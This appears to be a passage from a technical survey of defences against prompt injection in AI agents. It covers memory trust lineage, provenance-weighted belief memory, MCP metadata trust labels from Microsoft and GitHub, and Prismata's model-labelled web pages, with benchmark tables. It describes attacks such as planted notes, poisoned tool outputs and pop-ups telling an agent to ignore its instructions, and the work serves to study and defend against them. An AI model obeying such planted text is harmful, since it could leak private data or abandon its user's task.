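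Item labels are accurate only if the software splits text where its source changes. If it splits saved text every few hundred words instead, one item may contain the end of the user's note and the start of a stranger's email she pasted below it. Labelling the item by its first line would make the email text trusted. Using the label of the least trusted part is safe, but it makes the end of her note untrusted.

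Agents also write new items, and correct boundaries don't determine how to label them. If an agent reads four notes and saves a summary, the summary has no obvious label. Ouyang and Hou therefore record a link from each new item to each item the agent had retrieved, weighted by how much the retrieved item influenced the new one. The weight can come from a judging model or from attention. If every link in a chain back to an untrusted source has a weight above a threshold, the new item is untrusted and can't justify a sensitive action.

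Weak links accumulate as summaries build on summaries. In one of Ouyang and Hou's simulations the estimated weight starts at 0.9 and falls by 30% at each step:

| Step in the chain | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 | 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Weight of the link | 0.90 | 0.63 | 0.44 | 0.31 | 0.22 |

With a threshold of 0.30, the label survives four steps and disappears at the fifth, so a planted instruction becomes trusted after passing through enough summaries. Ouyang and Hou recommend a threshold of at most 0.10 for chains of five steps. A lower threshold also keeps more irrelevant links. At zero, each summary inherits the label of everything the agent retrieved, which amounts to session taint for anything built from memory.

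In its main test, MemLineage stopped all three kinds of memory attack, while checking only who had written each item stopped one. The test used fixed, simulated behaviour instead of a real model, so it shows that the rule works when the weights are reasonable, but not how often a real model would estimate reasonable weights. NeuroTaint, which saves labels alongside stored text and restores them on retrieval, found 28 of the 30 TaintBench cases in which content crossed between sessions or agents.

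### Poison relayed by a trusted tool

The label also depends on what the tools read. Singh (2026) tested this in *When Does Belief-Based Agent Memory Help?* with a memory that stores probabilities for each fact, such as which database a project uses. The memory weights each new claim by its reliability, which is the lower of two scores, one for the trustworthiness of its channel and one for how confident its wording sounds. The channel score matters because attackers control the wording. A false claim phrased as "Confirmed ... verified" scored 0.96 for confidence, compared with 0.25 for a hedged one.

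In a simulation, four trusted claims established a fact, and an attacker then sent false claims through a channel with a trust score of 0.2. The table shows how often the attacker changed the stored belief.

| How the memory decides | 1 false claim | 3 | 10 | 50 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Newest claim wins | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Majority wins | 0% | 0% | 100% | 100% |
| Trusts confident wording | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
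| Caps trust by channel | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

With two possible values, a claim of reliability *r* multiplies the odds of the value it asserts by *r*/(1 − *r*). At 0.2 that factor is a quarter, so even fifty false claims failed because each one raised the probability the memory gave to the true value. The protection fails once a channel's score rises above about 0.55. Taken literally, the formula would also let an attacker discredit a true belief by repeating it on a channel with a score below 0.5.

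Singh then sent the same false claims through a trusted tool that had taken in the attacker's data. The memory gave the claims the tool's high trust score, and the attack succeeded every time. When the simulation instead gave them the score of their original source, the attack never succeeded. Singh calls tracking the original source a hard requirement of the defence, but did not build the tracking and assumed that the software knew the source. Singh also assigned the trust scores by hand.

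The result applies to agents that use tools written by other people. A company's search tool may be reliable and still return a page that a stranger edited, so a single label for the whole tool would not show where the page came from.

Capping trust also lowers accuracy when the distrusted channel carries correct information. When Singh sent true corrections through a channel with a trust score of 0.3, accuracy fell from 100% to 54% on average, and to 21% in the noisiest setting.

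### Attacks that change only whether an action happens

Even perfect data tracking can miss an attack that stops an agent from acting. Suppose a user tells her agent to run the nightly backup unless there is a reason not to. A stranger's note in the agent's memory says that the storage system is under maintenance, so the agent skips the backup. No text from the note reaches any tool. NeuroTaint tests whether an action would have happened anyway, but only when the agent makes a call, and OpenAgentFlow checks only pending actions, so neither would check the decision to skip the backup.

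Garby and colleagues observe that guarantees ignoring control flow are weakest where data and control are interchangeable, and any text a language model reads can influence its actions.

Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, address the problem with two separate guarantees for an agent with long-term memory. In simplified form:

```
action integrity:
    every argument that reaches a sensitive tool is a value
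    the user typed or approved for that tool

reasoning integrity:
    if two runs have the same user input and randomness,
    and everything shown for approval, and every decision, is the same,
    then the agent behaves the same in both,
    whatever the untrusted memory contains
```

Action integrity alone would allow the skipped backup, because it covers only the arguments of calls the agent makes. Reasoning integrity rules out the skipped backup unless the note, or something derived from it, appeared at the approval step. If the note changed the agent's behaviour but not the approval step, two otherwise identical runs would differ.

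PerMIT gets this guarantee without estimating influence. The main model sees only names for untrusted memories, as in Willison's Dual LLM pattern, and a quarantined model searches the stored text. The main model can read an item only after a person or a checking model has approved its exact content. If the backup depends on the note, the note needs this approval first. The proofs treat every approved value as trusted, so they don't protect against a false note that gets approved.

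Jiang and colleagues checked the core of both proofs by computer. They also tested PerMIT on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which planted text has no effect until a later session. Models made the approval decisions in this test, and no attacks succeeded.

An approval applies to one exact value for one tool, and it isn't limited to one purpose or occasion. If a user approves her accountant's address for the email tool so that the agent can send an invoice, the agent may email that address again without asking. Any other address needs its own approval, even one the agent composed, unless the user typed it herself.

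## Who labels tool outputs in the Model Context Protocol

Every rule so far depends on someone having marked data as trusted or untrusted when it first arrived. In their benchmark tests, Costa and colleagues could mark the fields that the planted attacks targeted. A company has no list of the fields attackers will target, and its agents get data through tools that other people wrote. Many of those tools use MCP, which has no standard way to attach a trust label to a result.

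### Labels in a metadata field

In 2026 Microsoft and GitHub built a prototype that adds labels to MCP messages without changing the protocol. The messages have a field called `_meta` for extra information, and programs that don't recognise its contents can ignore them. The *client*, the program that runs the agent, puts labels there when it calls a tool. The *server*, the program that provides the tool, puts labels there when it returns a result. Each label has an address in JSONPath, a notation that points to one part of a structured message. This is Microsoft's sample call to post in a Teams channel, abridged and with shortened names:

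```
{
  "name": "SendMessageToChannel",
  "arguments": { "channelId": "...", "content": "..." },
  "_meta": {
    "com.github.ifc/labels": {
      "$": { "integrity": "untrusted",
             "confidentiality": "public" },
      "$.arguments.content": { "integrity": "trusted",
                               "confidentiality": ["user_1", "user_2"] }
    }
  }
}
```

The `$` stands for the whole call, so the first label records that the agent chose this call in an untrusted context. The second label covers only the text of the message, which two people may read. The channel has no label, so it inherits the whole call's label. Labels also pass upward, so a list without a label takes one from its labelled items.

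Servers can use the same field to advertise a policy for each tool. The policy is either a reference to a well-known rule or a short program in Rego, a language for access rules. The policy takes the labelled call as input and returns allow, deny or ask. One example is the Teams rule that checks a channel's members.

An MCP server's author can write both the labels on the data and the policy for the tool. That makes sense for Microsoft Teams, because Microsoft knows how its channels work. But a hostile server could advertise a policy that allows everything, so a client needs its own policies for servers it has no reason to trust.

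### GitHub's default labels

GitHub extended its MCP server to return labels when a user turns the feature on. Microsoft describes these labels as untrusted for public repositories and trusted for private ones, but GitHub's code, as documented on pkg.go.dev, labels the contents of issues untrusted in every repository because an attacker may control them. According to pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), this rule was already in the version of 18 May. An agent that works only on private repositories can therefore still lose its trusted context by reading an issue.

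| Result | Integrity | Confidentiality | Reason for the integrity label |
|---|---|---|---|
| Files in a public repository | Untrusted | Public | Anyone may have written them through a pull request |
| Files in a private repository | Trusted | Private | Only collaborators can add changes |
| Issues | Untrusted | Same as the repository | Attackers can control the text |
| Logs of automated jobs | Untrusted | Same as the repository | Logs repeat text from pull requests and downloads |
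| Published releases | Trusted | Same as the repository | Only collaborators can publish them |
| Security alerts | Untrusted | Private | Alerts quote suspicious code and other outside text |

Some of these choices depend on details that few outsiders would know. For example, a draft release is private even in a public repository, because only people who can push changes can see it.

GitHub's server gives a whole list one label. If a search matches ten public repositories and one private one, the server labels the entire result private. GitHub reasons that the items arrive together and the agent can then copy them all anywhere. Labels on individual items would be useful only to software that can keep the items apart, as Fides does.

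GitHub's MCP server and GitHub Agentic Workflows label some of the same text in opposite ways. The server marks a file on the main branch of a public repository untrusted, while Agentic Workflows gives it the highest level, `merged`. An issue in a private repository is untrusted to the server but `approved` in a workflow. The server's label depends on whether an outsider could have written the text, and the workflow's level depends on whether the project has accepted the text or its author. Both approaches are reasonable, but if a company uses both products, an instruction in a private issue will taint one agent and not the other.

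### Contractors and pasted text in private repositories

GitHub trusts private files because only collaborators can add to them. But a collaborator may be a contractor hired for a month and given access to only one repository. Suppose the contractor, or someone who has taken over the contractor's account, adds a file with a planted instruction. If a senior developer then asks her agent to review that repository, the agent may read the instruction while it has her access to everything else.

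The server labels the file trusted and private, so the agent's context stays trusted. The instruction tells the agent to open a second private repository and publish a file from it. The policy Microsoft describes for Copilot CLI blocks public posts from a context that is both untrusted and private. This context is trusted, so the policy doesn't stop the post.

Pasted text causes the same error without bad faith, as it does with GitHub's author filter. A developer might commit a customer's email as test data, or copy in another project's code with its README. Releases have this weakness even in public repositories. GitHub can draft release notes from the titles of merged pull requests, so an outsider's words can end up in a result the server labels trusted.

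A company could reduce the problem by treating folders for test data and copied code as untrusted. It would have to add that rule itself, because the server's labelling function's only input is whether the repository is private.

### Four possible labellers

The parties that could assign labels differ in what they can know, how they benefit from marking data as more trusted or more public than it should be, and whether they bear the consequences of a mistake.

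| Labeller | Information it has | Benefit of a generous label | Who bears a mistake |
|---|---|---|---|
| The server's author | Where each field comes from, but not who the user's colleagues are | A tool that interrupts people less. For a hostile author, a way in | The user and her employer |
| The deploying organisation | Its staff, partners and secrets, but not always how the tool works | Fewer approvals and complaints | The organisation |
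| The client, using the server's hints | What the agent has read so far, and what each server declares | A smoother product than a competitor's | The user |
| A model | The text itself, or the structure around it | None for the model, but a smoother product for the company that runs it | The user |

The deploying organisation is the only party that both assigns labels and is harmed when they are wrong. This is a good reason to let it overrule other parties' labels, but not to make it write every label itself.

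### What the specification says about servers

MCP lets a server attach short descriptions, called *annotations*, to its tools. MCP's July 2026 specification, *Tools* (2026), requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from trusted servers, and lets the client decide which servers to trust.

A March post by Model Context Protocol (2026) explains how the rule came about. During the original review, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a client could use a flag that it can't trust. Basil Hosmer, another participant, argued that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. The compromise was to call every annotation a hint and let each client decide how much weight to give it. In practice, most clients trust any server the user has installed, so a user who installs a server because its description looks useful also accepts the server's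 claims about itself.

The rule covers annotations, and Microsoft's labels are in `_meta`, so its wording doesn't strictly apply to them. Its reasoning still applies to labels that loosen restrictions, because a false claim that data is trusted can let an attack through. A client can safely accept an unknown server's claim that its data is untrusted or private, since a false claim at worst means some extra approvals for the user. A cautious client could therefore let any server make a label stricter, but let only servers the organisation has vetted make it looser.

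The March post proposes a similar test for new annotations. An annotation that is useful only when it is true is a contract and belongs in the software that enforces access, not among the hints. Of the labels "trusted" and "untrusted", only "untrusted" can be a hint by that test.

### Proposals for standard labels

Five proposals for new annotations or related features were open in March 2026. GitHub and OpenAI wrote the one on trust and sensitivity, SEP-1913, after finding gaps while using MCP in their own products. Under its rules, described in a Model Context Protocol (2026) post dated 13 March, servers would annotate each response as well as each tool, and a session's sensitivity could rise but never fall. This would make a form of session taint part of the protocol. Three of the other proposals would each add a single flag, for unsafe output, secrets or trust.

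No proposal for trust or flow labels had become part of the Model Context Protocol standard by late November, when the protocol's index of accepted and final proposals listed none. One such proposal, SEP-1913, was still a draft in July, according to the protocol's page for its interest group on annotations. The group can recommend changes but not make them.

Microsoft plans to seek agreement on its own scheme, and the March post suggests testing such ideas in `_meta` first. Keys in that field can begin with a vendor's own prefix, and the Model Context Protocol reserves certain prefixes for official use. The prototype's key, `com.github.ifc`, doesn't use a reserved prefix. A client that doesn't support the key will ignore it, so an agent built on that client will get the data without the warning.

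### Labels inferred from tool hints

Without standard labels, a client can still use the hints that MCP has had since March 2025. There are four, apart from a display title:

| Hint | Meaning when true | Assumed if the server leaves it out |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool changes nothing | False |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may destroy something, not just add to it | True |
| `idempotentHint` | The client can safely repeat the same call | False |
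| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside entities | True |

Microsoft suggests how a client could turn them into labels and policies:

```
policies
    read-only and closed-world    allow
    read-only and open-world      allow if every argument is public
    destructive                   ask the user

labels on results
    start from the labels of all the arguments
    open-world tool               add "untrusted"
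    tool that requires a login    add "private"
```

The second policy stops an agent from putting a stolen secret into the URL of a web page it fetches. If a server gives no hints, the client by default asks the user before every call and labels every result untrusted. Many servers leave the hints out, though, and some clients don't apply these defaults strictly.

The GitHub attack used a pull request, which the three policies may not cover. The tool that opens one isn't read-only, but an honest author can set `destructiveHint` to false because the tool only adds content. The client needs a fourth policy, which could cover pull requests, comments and email by treating every open-world tool that writes as a tool that sends data.

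Mail tools raise a different problem. The March post advises tool authors to set `openWorldHint` to false for tools with a closed domain, and an author could easily regard a user's own mailbox as one. Search results from the mailbox would then count as private and trusted, although strangers wrote much of the mail. The post acknowledges that "external" can mean outside the company or merely outside the user's computer, and it recommends treating anything that counts as external for a tool as a possible source of untrusted content, but this doesn't help if the tool's author considers the mailbox internal.

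The client or a gateway has to combine the labels, whoever supplies them. The July specification has no protocol-level session, so a server has no reliable way to link two calls to the same conversation, and it receives no record of what the agent read from other servers. A server also isn't allowed to change its list of tools because of earlier requests on the same connection, so it can't withdraw its posting tool once an agent has read a stranger's text. The SAMOS gateway starts a session when a client connects, so under the new specification it would need another way to identify which calls belong together.

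### The work per tool

An organisation that wants better labels than the hints provide can use the gateway that Microsoft published with its prototype. The gateway works with servers that know nothing about labels, but somebody has to supply three things for each tool: a schema describing the result, a Python function that assigns labels, and a policy. For a tool that searches mail, they might amount to this:

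```
schema      a list of messages, each with sender, recipients, subject, body

function    for each message:
                readers   = sender and recipients
                integrity = trusted if the sender is on the staff list,
                            otherwise untrusted

policy      allow, because the tool only reads
```

The function depends on a staff list that only the organisation has. The organisation may also have to write the schema, because MCP doesn't require servers to publish one. The server's author hasn't promised to keep to a schema the organisation wrote, so a later version of the server could rename `sender`. The function should then label the message untrusted instead of failing silently.

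Labelling whole tools takes much less work. SAMOS needs only two settings for each tool. Ntousakis thinks the tool's developer is best placed to choose them, and hopes eventually to infer them automatically from the tool's code and behaviour. But a fixed label on the mail tool would have to fit the worst message the tool could return, so every search would taint the session.

If a company connects five servers with 20 tools each, one label per tool means 100 decisions, or 200 settings in SAMOS, which one person could probably make in a day or two. Microsoft's gateway would need 100 schemas, 100 functions and 100 policies, although some tools could share a built-in policy. Microsoft doesn't estimate how long this would take.

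GitHub's code for a single server grew from four labelling functions in the May version to 17 in the later one. Most of them need only one or two facts, such as whether the repository is private, and some serve several tools. Those facts are enough to solve SAMOS's difficulty with `get_file_contents`, because the function checks at run time whether the repository is private. GitHub does this work once for all its users, while every organisation that runs the gateway has to do its own.

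### A model that labels web pages

Nobody can write a labelling function for every website. A shop's page mixes the shop's menus with customers' reviews and advertisements, and one button may buy an item while another posts a message. *Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) uses language models to label the regions of such pages while an agent browses.

A web page is a tree in which each element sits inside others. Suppose a user asks her agent to order a bow tie, and an attacker's review tells the agent to reset her password. Prismata works through the page like this:

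1. One model reads only the user's request and decides which kinds of content the task needs: the site's own, its users', its sellers' or outside content such as advertisements.
2. A labelling model goes down the tree from the top. It sees each element with the elements that contain it, but not what is inside or beside it. When it reaches a container marked "Customer Reviews", it labels everything inside as user content without reading further.
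3. For each button, link or form field, another model call sees only the user's request, the element and the chain of elements above it, and decides whether the task needs it.
4. Ordinary code applies the stricter result of steps 2 and 3. It removes content or makes it read-only, and refuses clicks on anything it has disabled.

The review isn't in the chain of elements above the password button, so it can't influence the decision to disable that button. The second step follows Biba's strict integrity rule. The model doesn't read down into content it hasn't labelled yet, and no element can get a more trusted label than its container. A wrong label can therefore do damage only in the part of the page below the planted text.

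The protection fails when planted text is in the chain above a control and there is no warning sign earlier on the page. In 5,664 pages from real sites, Villa and Tan found 90,408 pieces of untrusted content, of which 1,086 contained something an agent could click or fill in, and 94 of those had no warning sign before them. They describe this as about 0.1% of all the untrusted content, but it is 8.7% of the pieces that contained a control, which are the ones an attacker would look for. Language models also did the annotation behind these counts, so the counts may contain the same kinds of mistakes as the labels. Villa and Tan reduce the 94 cases to 15 by excluding ordinary links, which shouldn't change anything on a well-built site.

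The evaluation of Prismata used WebArena, a benchmark of simulated shops, forums and other sites, with GPT-5.4-mini as the agent. The attacks were pop-ups that offered a false shortcut, claimed the task was finished or told the agent to ignore its instructions. An attack succeeded if the agent clicked on or filled in the planted content.

| Attack | Tasks completed without Prismata | Tasks completed with Prismata | Attacks succeeding without Prismata | Attacks succeeding with Prismata |
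|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 29.9% | 26.6% | | |
| False shortcut | 11.2% | 24.4% | 63.9% | 2.1% |
| False completion | 2.3% | 24.8% | 92.5% | 0.0% |
| Ignore instructions | 0.0% | 19.9% | 100.0% | 0.0% |

On average, attack success fell from 85.5% to 0.7%. When there was no attack, the agent's task completion rate fell by 3.3 percentage points, or about one in nine of the tasks it could otherwise do.

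The pop-ups imitated advertisements, which few shopping or forum tasks need, so they were probably easy to label and remove. Even so, Prismata removed or disabled them only 93.1% of the time on average, and the agent ignored most of the rest on its own. The tests on WASP add little, because only one of the 42 end-to-end attacks worked without Prismata. Attacks adapted to the defence succeeded in 65% to 100% of cases without Prismata and never with it, but this test was small.

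Villa and Tan also compared the models' labels with a human expert's on 20 page views, four from each of five sites. The expert took about an hour to label each page view. For all six models, more than 93% of the elements that the model's labels left available to the agent would also have been available under the expert's labels. The figure was 98.69% for the most cautious model, GPT-5.4-nano, but its labels left available only 82.69% of the elements that the expert's labels would have.

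A score of 98.69% means that if the model leaves 200 elements available on a page, the expert would have withheld two or three of them. Villa and Tan acknowledge that one of these could be the element an attack needs. They used pages without attacks, so the comparison doesn't show how well the models label a page designed to mislead them. The expert could also make mistakes.

Over 20 tasks, the extra model calls raised the total duration of model requests from about 1,650 seconds to about 4,130. The price rose only from $1.11 to $1.62, because pages on the same site share much of their structure and Prismata can reuse earlier labels.

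Prismata doesn't address attacks that stay within the task. If the user wants the best-reviewed bow tie, the agent has to read the reviews, and a false review can still change what the agent buys.

The same method might work for MCP. Field names such as `reviews` and `body` work like headings, so a model could label a tool's output from its schema, once per tool, without reading any results. Nobody would need to write a labelling function, but the model would depend on field names that the server's author chose. Villa and Tan assume that the site itself is trustworthy, but a client can't assume that about every MCP server.
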